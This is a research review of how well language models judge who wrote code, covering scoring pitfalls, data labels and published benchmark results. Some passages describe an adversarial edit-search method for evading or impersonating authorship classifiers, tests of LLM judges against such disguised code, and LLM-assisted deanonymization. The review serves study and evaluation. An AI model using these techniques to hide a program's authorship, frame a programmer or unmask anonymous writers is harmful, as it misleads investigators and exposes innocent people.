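# How reliably language models judge who wrote code and why

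## What is judged and how the answers are scored

Code authorship analysis is the study of who, or what, wrote a piece of source code, the human-readable text of a program. *Authorship Attribution of Source Code* (Bogomolov, Kovalenko and colleagues, 2020) dates the field to 1989. For most of the time since, researchers trained a statistical classifier on labelled samples from the programmers they wanted to tell apart. Large language models, which learn from very large collections of text and code to write replies to a prompt, made a simpler method possible, in which researchers paste the code into the prompt and ask who or what wrote it. This report calls a model that answers this way, without training for the task, a judge.

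Teachers who suspect plagiarism, employers who set coding tests and analysts who trace malware all have reasons to ask a language model to judge who wrote a piece of code. The model will usually give a verdict with a plausible explanation, whether or not the verdict is right. To find out how often it is right, a researcher needs a record, independent of the model, of who or what wrote each piece of code.

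### The questions

Authorship verification means deciding whether two programs have the same author. Authorship attribution means choosing one author from a list of candidates, which gets harder as the list grows. A blind guess is right a third of the time with three candidates but only 0.4% of the time with 250. Researchers call attribution closed-world if the true author is certain to be on the list, and open-world if the correct answer may be "none of these".

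In human-or-machine detection, the judge decides whether a person or a language model wrote the code. If a model did, the judge can also be asked which one. Orel, Azizov and colleagues (2026) gathered code from 77 models for *AICD Bench*, but ask only which of 11 families, such as Llama or Qwen, the model belongs to. They argue that naming individual models becomes less practical as the number of models grows. Self-recognition is a special case in which the judge has to tell its own output from that of others.

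Behaviour is what a program does when it runs, purpose is what its author wanted it to do, and motive is why the author wanted that. Suppose a script deletes every log file older than thirty days from a server. Anyone can observe the deletion by running the script on a copy of the server. The purpose may have been to free disk space or to destroy the traces of a break-in, and someone who wanted the traces gone may have acted for money or out of loyalty to a friend. The script could be identical in every case. A mistake can also make behaviour differ from purpose. If the author typed the comparison the wrong way round, the script deletes the new logs and keeps the old ones.

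### Why style can identify a programmer

Programmers can solve the same problem with different code. They can write a loop with `for` or `while`, for example, and put a calculation in one long function or six short ones. They make many such choices, largely out of habit, and code stylometry measures those habits.

Caliskan-Islam, Harang and colleagues (2015), in *De-anonymizing Programmers via Code Stylometry*, sorted features of coding style into three kinds. Layout features describe how the text is arranged, such as whether it uses tabs or spaces, the proportion of whitespace, and whether an opening brace gets its own line. Lexical features are mostly counts of words and symbols, such as the number of comments or functions relative to the file's length. Syntactic features come from the abstract syntax tree, which represents how a program's statements and expressions nest inside one another.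 They include the depth of the tree and the pairs of adjacent constructs in it. Reformatting a file or deleting its comments does not change its syntactic features.

The researchers turned each file into a long row of such numbers and used the rows to train a random forest, a collection of decision trees that vote on the answer. They had nine files from each of 250 contestants in a programming competition, all solving the same nine problems. After training on eight files per person, the classifier identified the author of the ninth correctly about 95% of the time. With 1,600 contestants, accuracy was still about 93%. In a smaller trial with 62 programmers, accuracy was 96% with syntactic features alone and 89% with all the other features together. This comparison does not cleanly separate structure from wording, because the syntactic features also included counts of the words at the ends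 of the syntax tree's branches, such as variable names.

### Where the known answer comes from

The competition was Google Code Jam, and its archive is a very common source of code with known authors. Every entrant works on the same problems under an account name, which helps keep a classifier from mistaking what the code does for how its author writes. Caliskan-Islam and colleagues give the example of a project where Bob writes the user interface and Alice writes the network code. A classifier could tell their code apart by subject matter without learning anything about either person's style.

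Contest files have faults of their own. Mächtle, Serr and colleagues (2024) point out in *OCEAN* that many contain automatically generated comments with an `@author` tag, and if the tag is left in, attribution only requires reading a name. An entrant may also paste in a template that somebody else wrote. Contestants work alone and don't follow a style guide, so Caliskan-Islam and colleagues could not test how collaboration or a style guide affects the result.

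Public repositories, which are online project folders with a recorded history of changes, hold more ordinary code. If a repository lists a single contributor, the researcher credits that person with everything in it. This is wrong wherever the contributor copied a function from a forum, uploaded a colleague's work or accepted a coding assistant's suggestions. A subtler problem arises when each author appears in the data with one project, because the project's vocabulary and the libraries it uses then identify the author as well as any personal habit does. Bogomolov and colleagues trained models that told 40 such authors apart with 98% accuracy, but accuracy fell to 22% in a more realistic set-up with 21 developers.

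In shared projects, the version-control system logs who changed each line. The standard command for reading this log, `git blame`, returns only the last person to touch a line, so someone who merely re-indents a file can be recorded as its author. Dauber, Caliskan and colleagues (2017), in *Git Blame Who?*, acknowledge this weakness in their own labels, and they also had to remove renamed accounts and accounts shared by a group. Mächtle and colleagues instead used a tool that takes the whole editing history into account. Functions in their two collections had 1.54 and 2.19 authors on average, so a function often has no single author. Pair programming and edits after code review make authorship even harder to establish. Bogomolov and colleagues contacted developers to settle which e-mail aliases belonged to the same person, and they kept only newly created methods, because a modified method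 has no sole author.

How much do wrong labels matter? Dauber and colleagues took contest code by 250 authors and deliberately swapped the names on some of the files. For small amounts of swapping, their classifier lost about as much accuracy as the share of labels they had spoiled. For a judge on a yes-or-no question one can work it out directly. If a share $e$ of the labels is wrong at random, a judge whose true accuracy is $a$ will appear to have an accuracy of

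$$a(1-e) + (1-a)e.$$

With 5% of the labels wrong at random, a perfect judge scores 95% and a judge that is right 90% of the time scores 86%. Real labelling errors aren't random, so their effect is harder to predict. For example, if an assistant wrote some of the files labelled "human", a judge that correctly calls them machine-written loses marks.

That risk is specific to human-or-machine detection, where the two halves of the record differ in quality. The machine half is easy to record because the researcher prompts a model, saves the output and logs the model's name. The human half usually depends on dates. Patterson, Wang and Faulkner (2026), in *HybridCodeAuthorship*, start from a 2019 collection of GitHub code, which they say people generally believe to be human because it predates the assistants. *MultiAIGCD* (2025) draws its 33,286 human samples from CodeNet, an IBM dataset from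 2021. Orel, Paul and colleagues (2025), in *Droid*, did not exclude later code, and they concede that some of their "human" samples may contain a model's work. They therefore dropped from training the 7% of human samples about which a preliminary classifier was least certain. This is a reasonable way to clean training data but a risky way to clean test data, since it would also remove code by people who happen to write like machines, whom a detector is most likely to accuse wrongly.

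An accurate generation log does not always settle who wrote a program, because a person and a model may both have contributed. In some *Droid* samples, a model continued a human program after the first 10 to 85% of its lines; in others, it filled a gap or rewrote all of it. AICD Bench includes 100,000 programs that Llama 3.3 70B produced by rewriting human code. Orel and colleagues put these cases in a separate class, "hybrid", while Patterson and colleagues label each line as human or AI. Both choices are defensible, but a judge that may answer only "human" or "machine" for the whole file cannot be right. A model can also reproduce from memory a passage that a person wrote, and the log will list the model as the author.

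Records of why code was written are weaker than records of who wrote it. The best is a specification written before the code, such as a contest problem or a written task. Even then, the programmer may have misread it or had a further aim that it does not mention. A description derived from the finished code is much weaker evidence. Much of the code in *Droid* came without instructions, so *Droid* used a language model to read each program and write an instruction that would lead to similar code. This works well for generating new samples, but using the instructions as a record of what the original author wanted would be circular, because one model's reading of the code would be used to score another's.

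A seeded bug is a fault that a researcher plants on purpose, so it is known to be deliberate, but the same file may hold accidental faults that nobody has labelled. The code itself cannot establish its author's motive. A confession or a court's finding comes closest to a record of motive, and an experimenter can also assign one by instructing someone to write code for a stated reason. A malware label is a poor substitute because it means only that analysts found a program's behaviour harmful, and a criminal and a hired security tester may use the same program.

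### What running the code can settle

A computer can check correctness, however. For example, it can run a sorting function on some lists and compare the output with the expected result. Patterson and colleagues checked their human-written files and the AI-modified versions this way, using the projects' own unit tests, which are small programs that each check one part of the code. These results could also be wrong. A correct file could fail because an old library was missing, and a faulty one could pass because it only had to clear all the tests in any one relevant test file. Such mistakes can be fixed, for example by installing the missing library and running the test again.

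Running code doesn't reveal who wrote it, since a correct sorting function returns the same list whether a student, a professional or a model wrote it. This makes a judge's errors about authorship harder to catch than its errors about quality. Anyone can check a verdict on correctness by running the code, but a verdict on authorship can only be checked against a record of who wrote it. Even errors about quality are common. *CodeJudgeBench* (Jiang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) tested 26 models as judges of competing solutions, repairs and unit tests, and found that their verdicts shifted with the order of the answers, the names of variables and misleading comments.

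### Scores, and how a constant answer can earn them

On a yes-or-no question every verdict falls into one of four boxes. Let "same author" be the positive class. A true positive (TP) is then a "yes" about a pair that does share an author, and a false positive (FP) is a "yes" about a pair that does not. A true negative (TN) is a correct "no", and a false negative (FN) is a "no" about a pair with one author. Accuracy is the share of verdicts that are correct:

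$$\text{accuracy} = \frac{TP+TN}{TP+TN+FP+FN}$$

Balanced accuracy is the mean of the accuracies on the two classes:

$$\text{balanced accuracy} = \frac{1}{2}\left(\frac{TP}{TP+FN} + \frac{TN}{TN+FP}\right)$$

F1 combines precision, the share of "yes" verdicts that are correct, with recall, the share of positive items that the judge finds:

$$F_1 = \frac{2 \times \text{precision} \times \text{recall}}{\text{precision}+\text{recall}} = \frac{2\,TP}{2\,TP+FP+FN}$$

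The Matthews correlation coefficient (MCC) uses all four boxes and runs from −1 to 1, with 0 for verdicts that have no relation to the truth:

$$\text{MCC} = \frac{TP \times TN - FP \times FN}{\sqrt{(TP+FP)(TP+FN)(TN+FP)(TN+FN)}}$$

In *I Can Find You in Seconds!* (Choi, Tan and colleagues, 2025), one model produced 7 true positives, 93 false negatives, 100 true negatives and no false positives. Its accuracy is 107/200, or 53.5%. Its MCC is (7 × 100 − 0 × 93) / √(7 × 100 × 100 × 193), which is about 700/3,676, or 0.19.

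The model's accuracy was 53.5%, close to chance, but it answered "yes" for only 7 of the 200 pairs, whereas random guessing would have produced about 100. It had a strong answering habit, a tendency to give one answer whatever the code. All seven "yes" answers were correct, which would happen less than 1% of the time if they had been assigned to pairs at random. So the model did pick up something about authorship, but its habit of answering "no" kept most of that from showing in its accuracy.

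A judge can also score respectably on habit alone:

| Verdicts | Accuracy | Balanced accuracy | F1 | MCC |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The model above | 53.5% | 53.5% | 0.13 | 0.19 |
| Always "no", a third of items positive | 66.7% | 50% | 0 | 0 |
| Always "yes", half of items positive | 50% | 50% | 0.67 | 0 |

When a judge always gives the same answer, the MCC formula gives zero divided by zero, which researchers count as 0 by convention. The judge in the second row doesn't need to look at the code to be right about all the negatives, which make up two thirds of the test. The judge in the third row doesn't need to look at the code either, and its precision of 0.5 and recall of 1 give an F1 score of 2 × 0.5 × 1 / 1.5 = 0.67.

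F1 also depends on which class counts as positive. If "different authors" is the positive class in the worked example, the same 200 verdicts give an F1 of 0.68 instead of 0.13, while the MCC stays at 0.19. Choi and colleagues prefer the MCC because language models tend to agree with a claim in the prompt, and F1 doesn't count correct negatives. Orel and colleagues use macro-F1 in AICD Bench, which is the average of the F1 scores for each class. The judge that always answers "yes" scores 0.33 on macro-F1, compared with 0.67 on F1.

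Scores also depend on the make-up of the test set. *Code Detectors Have a Half-Life* (2026) uses 18 human solutions and 126 machine-written ones, 18 from each of seven generators, with "human" as the positive class. A judge that always answers "human" gets an F1 of 0.67 when tested against one generator at a time, but would get 0.22 against all seven pooled. A judge that always answers "machine" would reach 87.5% accuracy on the pooled set. Changing the verdict on just one of the 18 human solutions moves recall by more than five points.

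The proportions of human and machine-written code change again outside the laboratory. Suppose a judge correctly classifies 90% of human-written files and 90% of machine-written ones, and a teacher runs it on 100 assignments, five of them written by a model. On average, it will flag 4.5 of the five machine-written assignments and 9.5 of the 95 human-written ones. About two in three flags will then be wrong, even though balanced accuracy is still 90%.

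Judges sometimes decline to answer, and researchers have to decide how to score those refusals. Choi and colleagues count "unsure" as wrong. Under that rule, a judge that answers only ten of 200 pairs, five from each class, and gets all ten right would have an accuracy of 5% and an MCC of −0.90. A judge that answers every question and is nearly always wrong could have the same MCC. Readers can tell the two apart only if the researchers also report how many questions went unanswered.

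### Contamination

No scoring formula can distinguish a model that compares coding styles from one that has already seen the answers. Contamination is the presence of test material in a model's training data. Google Code Jam solutions have been public since 2008, so a model trained on a contestant's files might recognise them or the name attached to them. This would inflate its score on that archive but would not help it judge code by an unfamiliar author.

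The usual precaution is to use recent data. Choi and colleagues collected part of theirs from GitHub repositories with commits between May and October 2024 and ran the experiments that November. This protection is temporary, since a model trained in 2026 may well have seen code from 2024. The code may also have circulated elsewhere for years before it was committed. AICD Bench instead adds 50,000 human-written samples from The Heap, a collection released as contamination-free that does not overlap with The Stack, a large public body of code. This rules out The Stack as a source of contamination, but not other code that a company used in training without disclosing it.

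Using recent code also makes the "human-written" label less reliable. A program from last month is probably new to the judge, but an AI assistant may have written half of it. Older code avoids this problem, since a program from 2015 is almost certainly a person's work, but it may well be in the training data of every judge one might test. To be sure that a person wrote the code and that the judge hasn't seen it, a researcher would need to watch people write new programs with the assistant switched off.

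## Did the same programmer write both programs?

Choi and colleagues tested eight language models on this question in November 2024. Their results apply to models of that year, such as GPT-4o and Gemini 1.5 Pro, which newer systems have since replaced. They took their method from research on ordinary prose. *Can Large Language Models Identify Authorship?* (2024) had already tested whether models could identify who wrote a set of blog posts and e-mails without being trained for the task. The models did better when the prompt listed which features of language to look at, and generally did worse when the number of candidate writers rose from 10 to 20.

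### Pairs of contest programs

The simplest test used 200 pairs of C++ programs from Google Code Jam. The same contestant had written both programs in 100 of the pairs, and different contestants had written them in the other 100. Choi and colleagues tried three zero-shot prompts, meaning prompts with no labelled examples. Averaged over the three, GPT-4o was right 87.2% of the time and Gemini 1.5 Pro 85.7%. With only 200 pairs, the margin of error is about 4.6 percentage points either way, so the 1.5-point gap doesn't show which model is better. Both scored far above the 50% expected from guessing.

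Layout and subject matter can't easily explain these scores. The files come from a collection of 1,632 programs by 204 contestants that Quiring, Maier and Rieck (2019) prepared for *Misleading Authorship Attribution of Source Code using Adversarial Learning*. They ran every file through an automatic formatter, which removed personal habits of indentation and brace placement. They also expanded macros, the private abbreviations that some contestants define to save typing. Each contestant solved the same eight problems once, so two files by one person always solve different problems, and a judge can't find the same-author pairs by looking for programs that do the same thing. The remaining clues are the choice of names, data types, library functions and ways of dividing up a task. The solutions may also have been in the models' training data, since they had been public for about seven years.

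Other models gave the same answer for almost every pair, regardless of the code. Llama 2 7B answered "same author" and GPT-3.5 answered "different authors", so both scored close to 50%. But if a teacher used them to compare each new assignment with the student's earlier work, she would clear nearly everyone with Llama 2 7B, including students who had paid somebody else to do the assignment, and accuse nearly everyone with GPT-3.5.

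Llama 3 8B had a Matthews correlation coefficient (MCC) of about −0.9, mostly because the researchers counted its many missing answers as errors. Reversing the answers it did give would therefore not make it a good judge.

### Choosing from a list of suspects

Choi and colleagues then gave the models a program and sample code from 3 to 10 candidates, and asked which candidate had written the program. This is few-shot prompting, because each sample is labeled with its author. In half of the cases, the true author was not among the candidates, so the right answer was "none of them". The best MCC they report is 0.77, almost the same as the 0.78 for pairs.

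GPT-4o cannot have achieved that score on Java, where it wrongly named one of the candidates in 82 to 91 of the 100 cases where the author was not among them. Even if it had picked the right person every time the author was present, its accuracy would have been between 54.5% and 59%, and its MCC at most 0.31.

This matters a great deal in an investigation, because investigators rarely know that the culprit is on their list. Let $p$ be the probability, before anyone consults the judge, that the author is among the suspects. Let $f$ be the share of absent-author cases in which the judge names somebody anyway. If we generously assume that the judge always picks the right person when the author is present, the probability that a named suspect wrote the code is

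$$\frac{p}{p + f(1-p)}.$$

With $f = 0.82$, the lowest of GPT-4o's Java figures, a starting probability of 50% rises only to 55%, and one of 10% rises to 12%. GPT-4o's answer is therefore very weak evidence that the police's list includes the author, and even if it does, the answer may identify the wrong person on it.

Asking about each suspect separately, as in the test with pairs, could still often match the code to an innocent person. GPT-4o was wrong about 13% of the time in that test. Suppose its errors fell equally on same-author and different-author pairs and that its mistakes about different suspects were independent. It would then match the code to at least one innocent suspect 34% of the time if there were three of them, and 75% of the time if there were ten. Separate questions would at least show an investigator when the judge had matched the code to several people, which is a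 useful warning.

*Large Language Models and Forensic Linguistics* (2025) cites the MCC of 0.78 as evidence that language models can strengthen authorship analysis. That figure fairly describes how GPT-4o and Gemini did on pairs of contest programs, but the rate of false accusations would be more useful to a forensic laboratory. The laboratory could measure that rate before any real case by giving the model lists of candidates known to leave out the author and counting how often it names someone.

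### A tournament with 500 programmers

A list of ten suspects fits easily into a prompt, but sample code from hundreds of programmers does not. Choi and colleagues got round the limit with a knockout tournament, in which each of 500 C++ programmers was represented by a single reference file. It works as follows:

1. Divide the 500 programmers into 42 groups, which makes about 12 in each. For each group, show the model the unknown program and the group's reference files, and ask which programmer is the likeliest author. The 42 winners go through.
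2. Divide the 42 winners into four groups and ask the same question about each group. Four programmers remain.
3. Put the four in one prompt. The model's choice is the final answer.

The procedure takes 47 prompts for each unknown program. It identified the right programmer 65 to 66% of the time, compared with 0.2% for a blind guess. On Java, with 686 programmers, the best result was 68.7%.

The true author has to win every round, so the final accuracy is the product of the success rates in the three rounds. A final accuracy of 65% means an average success rate of about 87% per round. But the rounds are not equally hard. A first-round group is a more or less arbitrary dozen, while the wrong programmers in the final got there because the model chose their code over that of everyone else in their part of the draw. The smallest group may therefore contain the closest rivals. A true author who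 is eliminated in the first round cannot return. Letting two programmers through from each group would reduce that risk but require more prompts.

The tournament also avoids the problem that GPT-4o had with absent authors. In the first round, the true author is in only one of the 42 groups, but the model has to advance someone from every group. The 41 wrong choices do no harm as long as the true author beats them later. Evidently, these models can often pick the closest match from a group. Recognising that the closest match is not the author is much harder, and the tournament doesn't require it. If the true author isn't among the 500, the procedure still ends with one name, and nothing in the result distinguishes it from a correct answer.

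### Style or project?

The tournament code came from GitHub repositories with a single contributor. Choi and colleagues do not report taking the unknown program and its author's reference file from different repositories. If both came from the same project, the model could have matched them by the project's vocabulary and libraries instead of by the programmer's style.

Bogomolov and colleagues measured how much this matters for trained classifiers, using the code of IntelliJ IDEA, a large programming tool with hundreds of contributors. They took about 348,000 methods (short named blocks of code) by 26 developers and divided each developer's work into training and test sets in nine different ways. The methods and developers stayed the same, and only the distance between the two sets changed, from files in neighbouring folders to files in distant parts of the project. When the classifiers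 could no longer rely on the surroundings of the code, they lost more than half of their correct answers. The neural network's accuracy fell from 48% to 22%, and the random forest's from 42.2% to 19.6%.

A judge with a single reference file has much less opportunity to learn a project's vocabulary than a classifier with thousands of methods, so it would be wrong to halve the tournament's 65%. But a judge needs only one distinctive shared name to make a match, and nobody knows how large the effect is. To measure it, a researcher could take the reference from one repository and the unknown program from another, for every programmer with at least two repositories, and see how far accuracy drops. Until someone does this, the tournament result is evidence that a model can connect files by the same person, and weaker evidence that it does so by style.

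The contest pairs don't have this fault, but contest programmers may be unusually easy to tell apart. In *Source Code Authorship Attribution Does Not Generalize from Competitions to Classrooms*, Yemets and Horváth (2026) trained one classifier, CodeBERT, on several collections of code. Among 1,000 Google Code Jam contestants, it named the right one 70.7% of the time. They then trained it on assignments at a technical university and tested it only on tasks it had not seen that student solve. Among 690 students doing closely specified exercises, it was right 0.2% of the time, compared with 0.14% for random guessing. Among 812 students who designed their own projects, it was right 0.06% of the time, which is below chance.

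A shortage of data probably explains part of this collapse. The contest authors were the most active in the archive, while the students had submitted only three or four programs each, and a classifier with a thousand possible answers needs more examples than that. A language model that judges from a prompt isn't trained on the students' programs, so it might do better. It would still face the other difficulties that Yemets and Horváth describe. Beginners' habits change from one assignment to the next, and whole classes build on the same template and lecturer's examples. Students who were free to design their own projects were no easier to identify, so narrow exercises can't be the whole explanation.

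In *Reassessing Code Authorship Attribution in the Era of Language Models* (2025), Dipongkor, Yao and Moran trained seven language models on 12,000 programs by 463 developers and found similar limits. Errors clustered in programs shorter than 200 tokens (the word fragments a model reads) and in problems where programmers seeking efficiency tend to reach the same solution. On solutions from LeetCode, a site for practising interview questions, accuracy was 64% for C++ and 94% for C#, although C++ made up 62% of the samples and C# only 2%. The researchers attribute the gap to C++ programmers having more similar styles. However, the C# samples came from only four programmers and the C++ samples from 142, which would make C# easier even if styles were equally varied in both languages.

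Ravich and Fire (2026) report more encouraging results for the Linux kernel in *Stylometric Defenses Against Author Impersonation in Software Repositories*. They trained a model to compare patches, the small changes that developers submit to a project, and tested it on developers it had never seen. A randomly chosen pair of patches by one developer got a higher similarity score than a randomly chosen pair by two developers about 93% of the time. Choi and colleagues asked the same question, but this test used real collaborative code. However, each patch came with an English message describing the change, and Ravich and Fire found that these messages contributed most to the average result. Kernel developers also tend to work on the same part of the system for years, so subject matter may have helped here too.

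Ravich and Fire use the scores to rank suspicious patches for a person to check. In 2021 an attacker added two malicious changes to the PHP programming language under the names of trusted developers, and their system placed both in the top 1.03% of the patches to review. A ranking suits this kind of evidence better than a verdict because a reviewer who finds nothing wrong with a patch can move on to the next without having accused anyone.

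### Disguised code

The programmers discussed so far had no reason to hide their identity, but someone who writes malware does. They might try evasion, which means altering the program so that a judge no longer connects it with them. They might also try imitation, which means altering it so that a judge connects it with a particular other person, who may then be blamed.

Quiring and colleagues built a program that does both. It can make 36 kinds of edits that change how code looks but leave what it does essentially the same. For instance, it can turn a `for` loop into a `while` loop, replace one printing function with another, or move the body of a loop into its own function. It doesn't change the layout or insert junk code, because the result has to look like something a programmer would write.

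The program uses the classifier it is attacking to choose its edits. It tries many sequences of up to five edits, submits each altered file to the classifier and gets a score for every candidate author. It then compares the sequences by their first edit, keeps the first edit with the best average scores and searches again from there. This method, Monte-Carlo tree search, is best known from programs that play Go. The attack stops when the classifier gives the desired answer or when further edits bring no improvement. Most successful evasions added, removed or changed fewer than five lines in files that averaged 74 lines.

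Quiring and colleagues attacked two classifiers: a random forest by Caliskan-Islam and colleagues and a neural network by other researchers. Imitation worked better when the attacker had two sample files by the programmer being imitated and could copy names and other habits from them.

| Trained classifier | Evasion succeeded | Imitation with samples | Imitation without samples |
|---|---|---|---|
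| Random forest | 99.2% | 77.3% | 71.2% |
| Neural network | 99.1% | 81.3% | 69.1% |

Choi and colleagues tested their judges on disguised programs from this line of work and concluded that language models are somewhat robust to such attacks. For comparison, they cite the success rates of 77 to 81% against trained classifiers, but those rates are only for imitation. The success rate for evasion is 99%.

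When the judge sees a pair of programs, the right answer depends on the attack. In an evasion, the same person wrote both the disguised program and the ordinary one, so the right answer is "same author". In an imitation, the disguised program is paired with a genuine one by the victim, so the right answer is "different authors". A judge that always says "different authors" would miss every evasion and get every imitation right, scoring 50% if there were equal numbers of each.

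The judges' overall accuracies, between 54% and 66%, were not far above that. Under the ordinary prompts, they missed between 44 and 88 of the 100 evasions. The judge that missed 88 evasions can have misjudged only about four of the 100 imitations in the other half of the test, because its overall accuracy was at least 54%. That overall figure doesn't show how much worse it did on evasions than on imitations.

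Some of these misses would have happened without any disguise. On the ordinary contest pairs, GPT-4o made about 26 errors in 200, so it missed at most 26 of the 100 same-author pairs on average, and Gemini 1.5 Pro missed at most 29. Once the code was disguised, every judge missed at least 44, while random guessing would miss about 50.

The attack succeeded less often against the judges (44 to 88%) than against the trained classifiers (99%), but the comparison isn't fair, for two reasons. The classifiers had to pick one author out of 204, so a small push towards any of the other 203 was enough to make them fail, while the judges had only two answers to choose from. More importantly, Quiring's program chose its edits using the classifiers' scores, without using a language model. An attacker who searched for edits that change GPT-4o's answer might succeed more often.

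Dipongkor and colleagues suggest what those edits might be. Most of the language models they trained for attribution were harder to fool than an older neural network, which the attacks fooled 42% of the time. The attacks that worked on the language models tended to change a larger portion of the code, by removing comments and unused code, adding print statements or rewriting functions and control flow. Quiring's edits rarely changed more than a few lines. These results are for trained models, so they may not apply exactly to models that are only prompted.

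The claim of robustness is therefore reasonable for imitation but wrong for evasion. Which matters more depends on how the judge is used. A court worried about framing an innocent programmer would benefit from a judge that seldom mistakes an imitation for the real author's work, provided that the judge isn't also choosing from a list of suspects. An analyst trying to link new malware to a known author needs a judge that can recognize the author's code even when it has been disguised, and these judges failed to do that about half the time or more.

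### Newer models

No published study appears to repeat these tests on human programmers with models from 2025 or 2026. In the closest experiment on code, *Style, Not Self*, Barkhordar and Thapa (2026) asked current commercial models about programs that other models had written. People differ from one another in ways that models may not, so these results don't establish how a current model would do on the contest pairs.

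Two more recent papers study prose. *Assessing Deanonymization Risks with Stylometry-Assisted LLM Agent* (2026) uses GPT-4.1, a model from April 2025, to identify who wrote anonymous articles. In one of its tests, half of the articles are by people who are not among the targets, the same precaution that exposed GPT-4o's false accusations on Java. *Author Representation Strategies for Zero-Shot Authorship Attribution* (2026) compares three ways of prompting a language model against a numerical method, which converts each text into a list of numbers describing its style and looks for the closest match. Prompts that gave only the candidates' labels were ineffective. Adding information about how each candidate writes helped consistently, but the numerical method, which first narrows down the candidates much as the tournament does, gave the best results overall. The paper concludes that current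 open-source language models are still not good enough for robust attribution. This is weak evidence about the strongest commercial models, and code offers different clues from prose, but it gives no reason to assume that the failures of 2024 have gone away by themselves.

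## Did a person or a machine write it?

In *Code Detectors Have a Half-Life*, a short conference paper from October 2026, Alberick Djire tested eight language models as judges, including GPT-5-mini and Claude Sonnet 5. Djire used the set of 18 human and 126 machine-written programs mentioned earlier. Human programmers and seven code generators, including ChatGPT, GitHub Copilot and StarCoder, had attempted the same six LeetCode problems in C++, Java and Python. The judges saw one program at a time and had to say whether a language model had written it, and why. Djire asked each question three times, averaged the results, and scored every generator against the same 18 human programs.

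### Eight judges and 18 human programs

The paper gives an accuracy and an F1 score for each comparison, with "human" as the positive class. With 18 programs on each side, those two figures are usually enough to work out how many programs a judge called human. The table gives these counts for seven of the judges under the plain zero-shot prompt. The counts are approximate because Claude and Gemini 3 seem to have occasionally skipped a program.

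| Judge | Accuracy, StarCoder | Accuracy, ChatGPT | Human programs called human | StarCoder programs called human | ChatGPT programs called human |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5 | 0.50 | 0.50 | 18 | 18 | 18 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 0.53 | 0.56 | 18 | 17 | 16 |
| Ministral 14B | 0.50 | 0.50 | 11 | 11 | 11 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.37 | 0.71 | 9 | 13 | 1 |
| Mistral Large | 0.56 | 0.53 | 2 | 0 | 1 |
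| Gemini 3 Flash | 0.14 | 0.50 | 1 | 14 | 0 |
| Llama 3.1 70B | 0.50 | 0.50 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

A good judge would have a high number in the first column of counts and low numbers in the other two, but none of these seven models does. GPT-3.5 and Gemini 2.5 called nearly everything human, and Llama called nearly everything machine-written. Ministral did not strongly favor either answer, but it called 11 of 18 programs human regardless of who wrote them, which is no better than guessing.

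Claude's verdicts did depend on the code. The human programs were the same in both comparisons, so the jump in accuracy from 0.37 to 0.71 comes entirely from the difference between StarCoder's code and ChatGPT's. Gemini 3 called 17 of the 18 human programs machine-written and 14 of StarCoder's 18 programs human. Reversing its answers would make 86% of them correct, so Gemini 3 did separate the two groups but swapped their labels. Judges make the same kind of swap between named models.

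One possible cause is a difference in correctness. The collection's creators ran all the programs and found that every human solution was correct, but only 26 of the 126 machine-written ones were. A judge could use bugs to separate the two groups, but it would get most labels backwards if it took bugs as a sign of a human author. Gemini 3's results partly fit this explanation. CodeWhisperer, Amazon's coding assistant, solved none of the tasks, and Gemini 3 called 16 of its 18 programs human. But ChatGPT solved only four tasks, and Gemini 3 called none of ChatGPT's programs human, so bugs can't be the whole explanation. Current models solve such problems far more reliably, so a judge's score on buggy code from 2023 is a poor guide to how it would do on their code.

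There are also only 18 human programs, so a judge that recognises 9 of them could have a true rate anywhere from about 29% to 71%. Testing against seven generators doesn't narrow this range, because the same 18 human programs appear every time.

### The best judge's missing answers

GPT-5-mini has by far the best scores in the paper, with a zero-shot F1 between 0.75 and 0.95 depending on the generator. Some of its other scores are impossible as they stand. With a longer prompt, it has an accuracy of 0.83 and an F1 of 0.40 on ChatGPT's code. Suppose it had answered for all 36 programs. For a given F1, accuracy is highest if the judge never calls a machine's program human. If $r$ is the share of human programs it recognises, then

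$$F_1 = \frac{2r}{1+r}, \qquad \text{accuracy} = \frac{1+r}{2}.$$

An F1 of 0.40 gives $r = 0.25$ and an accuracy of 0.625. Averaging over three runs could raise that ceiling to at most 0.70, still well below 0.83.

The figures do fit if GPT-5-mini gave a usable answer for only 18 of the 36 programs, with 15 right, 3 wrong and just one human program recognised. Djire doesn't mention missing answers, so this is a guess from the arithmetic. The zero-shot scores fit the same pattern, with 22 to 28 answers out of 36 and nine human programs recognised. If so, and if missing answers count as errors (the rule Choi and colleagues used), GPT-5-mini's zero-shot accuracy drops from 0.76–0.96 to about 0.47–0.75. It may still be the best of the eight judges, but the 0.95 isn't safe to quote without checking how many programs it covers.

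One of the longer prompts told the judge to examine comments, names and libraries before answering, another control flow and formatting, and a third wording and the program's apparent purpose. These prompts helped some judges and hurt others. Claude recognised 17 human programs instead of 9 when told to look at wording, and its accuracy on ChatGPT's code rose to 0.94, but it still called 15 of StarCoder's 18 programs human. Llama, which had recognised no human programs, recognised 13 when told to look at structure. It then called 15 of ChatGPT's programs human, but only 2 by InstructCodeT5+, a small open generator. A teacher who tested a prompt on one generator's code could not predict how well it would work on another's.

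Djire's title refers to a different claim, that dedicated detectors go out of date as code generators change. Two such detectors, GPT-Sniffer and DetectCodeGPT, classified every program as machine-written, and a third, GPT-Zero, was only slightly better than chance. Age doesn't explain these failures. The machine-written programs date from August and September 2023. GPT-Sniffer's developers published it in 2024 to recognise ChatGPT's code, but it failed here on ChatGPT's code from the year before. It transferred poorly from one collection of programs to another. To show ageing, a researcher would have to take a detector that works on one year's models and measure its accuracy on the next year's.

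### A larger test, and why odd human code looks artificial

Orel and colleagues tested two judges, Gemini 2.5 Flash and Gemma 3 27B, on tens of thousands of programs, a 5% sample of AICD Bench. One task was to label each program "human" or "AI". Another added two more labels, "hybrid" and "adversarial", the latter meaning code from a model that someone had prompted or trained to imitate a person. The remaining task was to name the model family, and both judges did about as well as guessing. The scores are macro-F1, multiplied by 100.

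| | Human or AI | Four choices |
|---|---|---|
| Random guessing | 45.7 | 20.3 |
| Gemini, plain prompt | 57.2 | 26.0 |
| Gemini, step-by-step prompt | 62.3 | 28.1 |
| Gemma, plain prompt | 58.5 | 22.2 |
| Gemma, step-by-step prompt | 54.9 | 22.2 |
| Best trained classifier | 43.1 | 61.7 |

Orel and colleagues write that step-by-step prompting consistently improves the results, but Gemma got worse at telling human code from AI code. The comparison also doesn't isolate the effect of reasoning, because the step-by-step prompt includes a long checklist of clues, which the researchers had Gemini summarise. The prompt tells the model to reason silently and reply with one word. Gemini 2.5 can work through a problem in hidden text before it replies, but Gemma 3 can't, so for Gemma the prompt was little more than the checklist.

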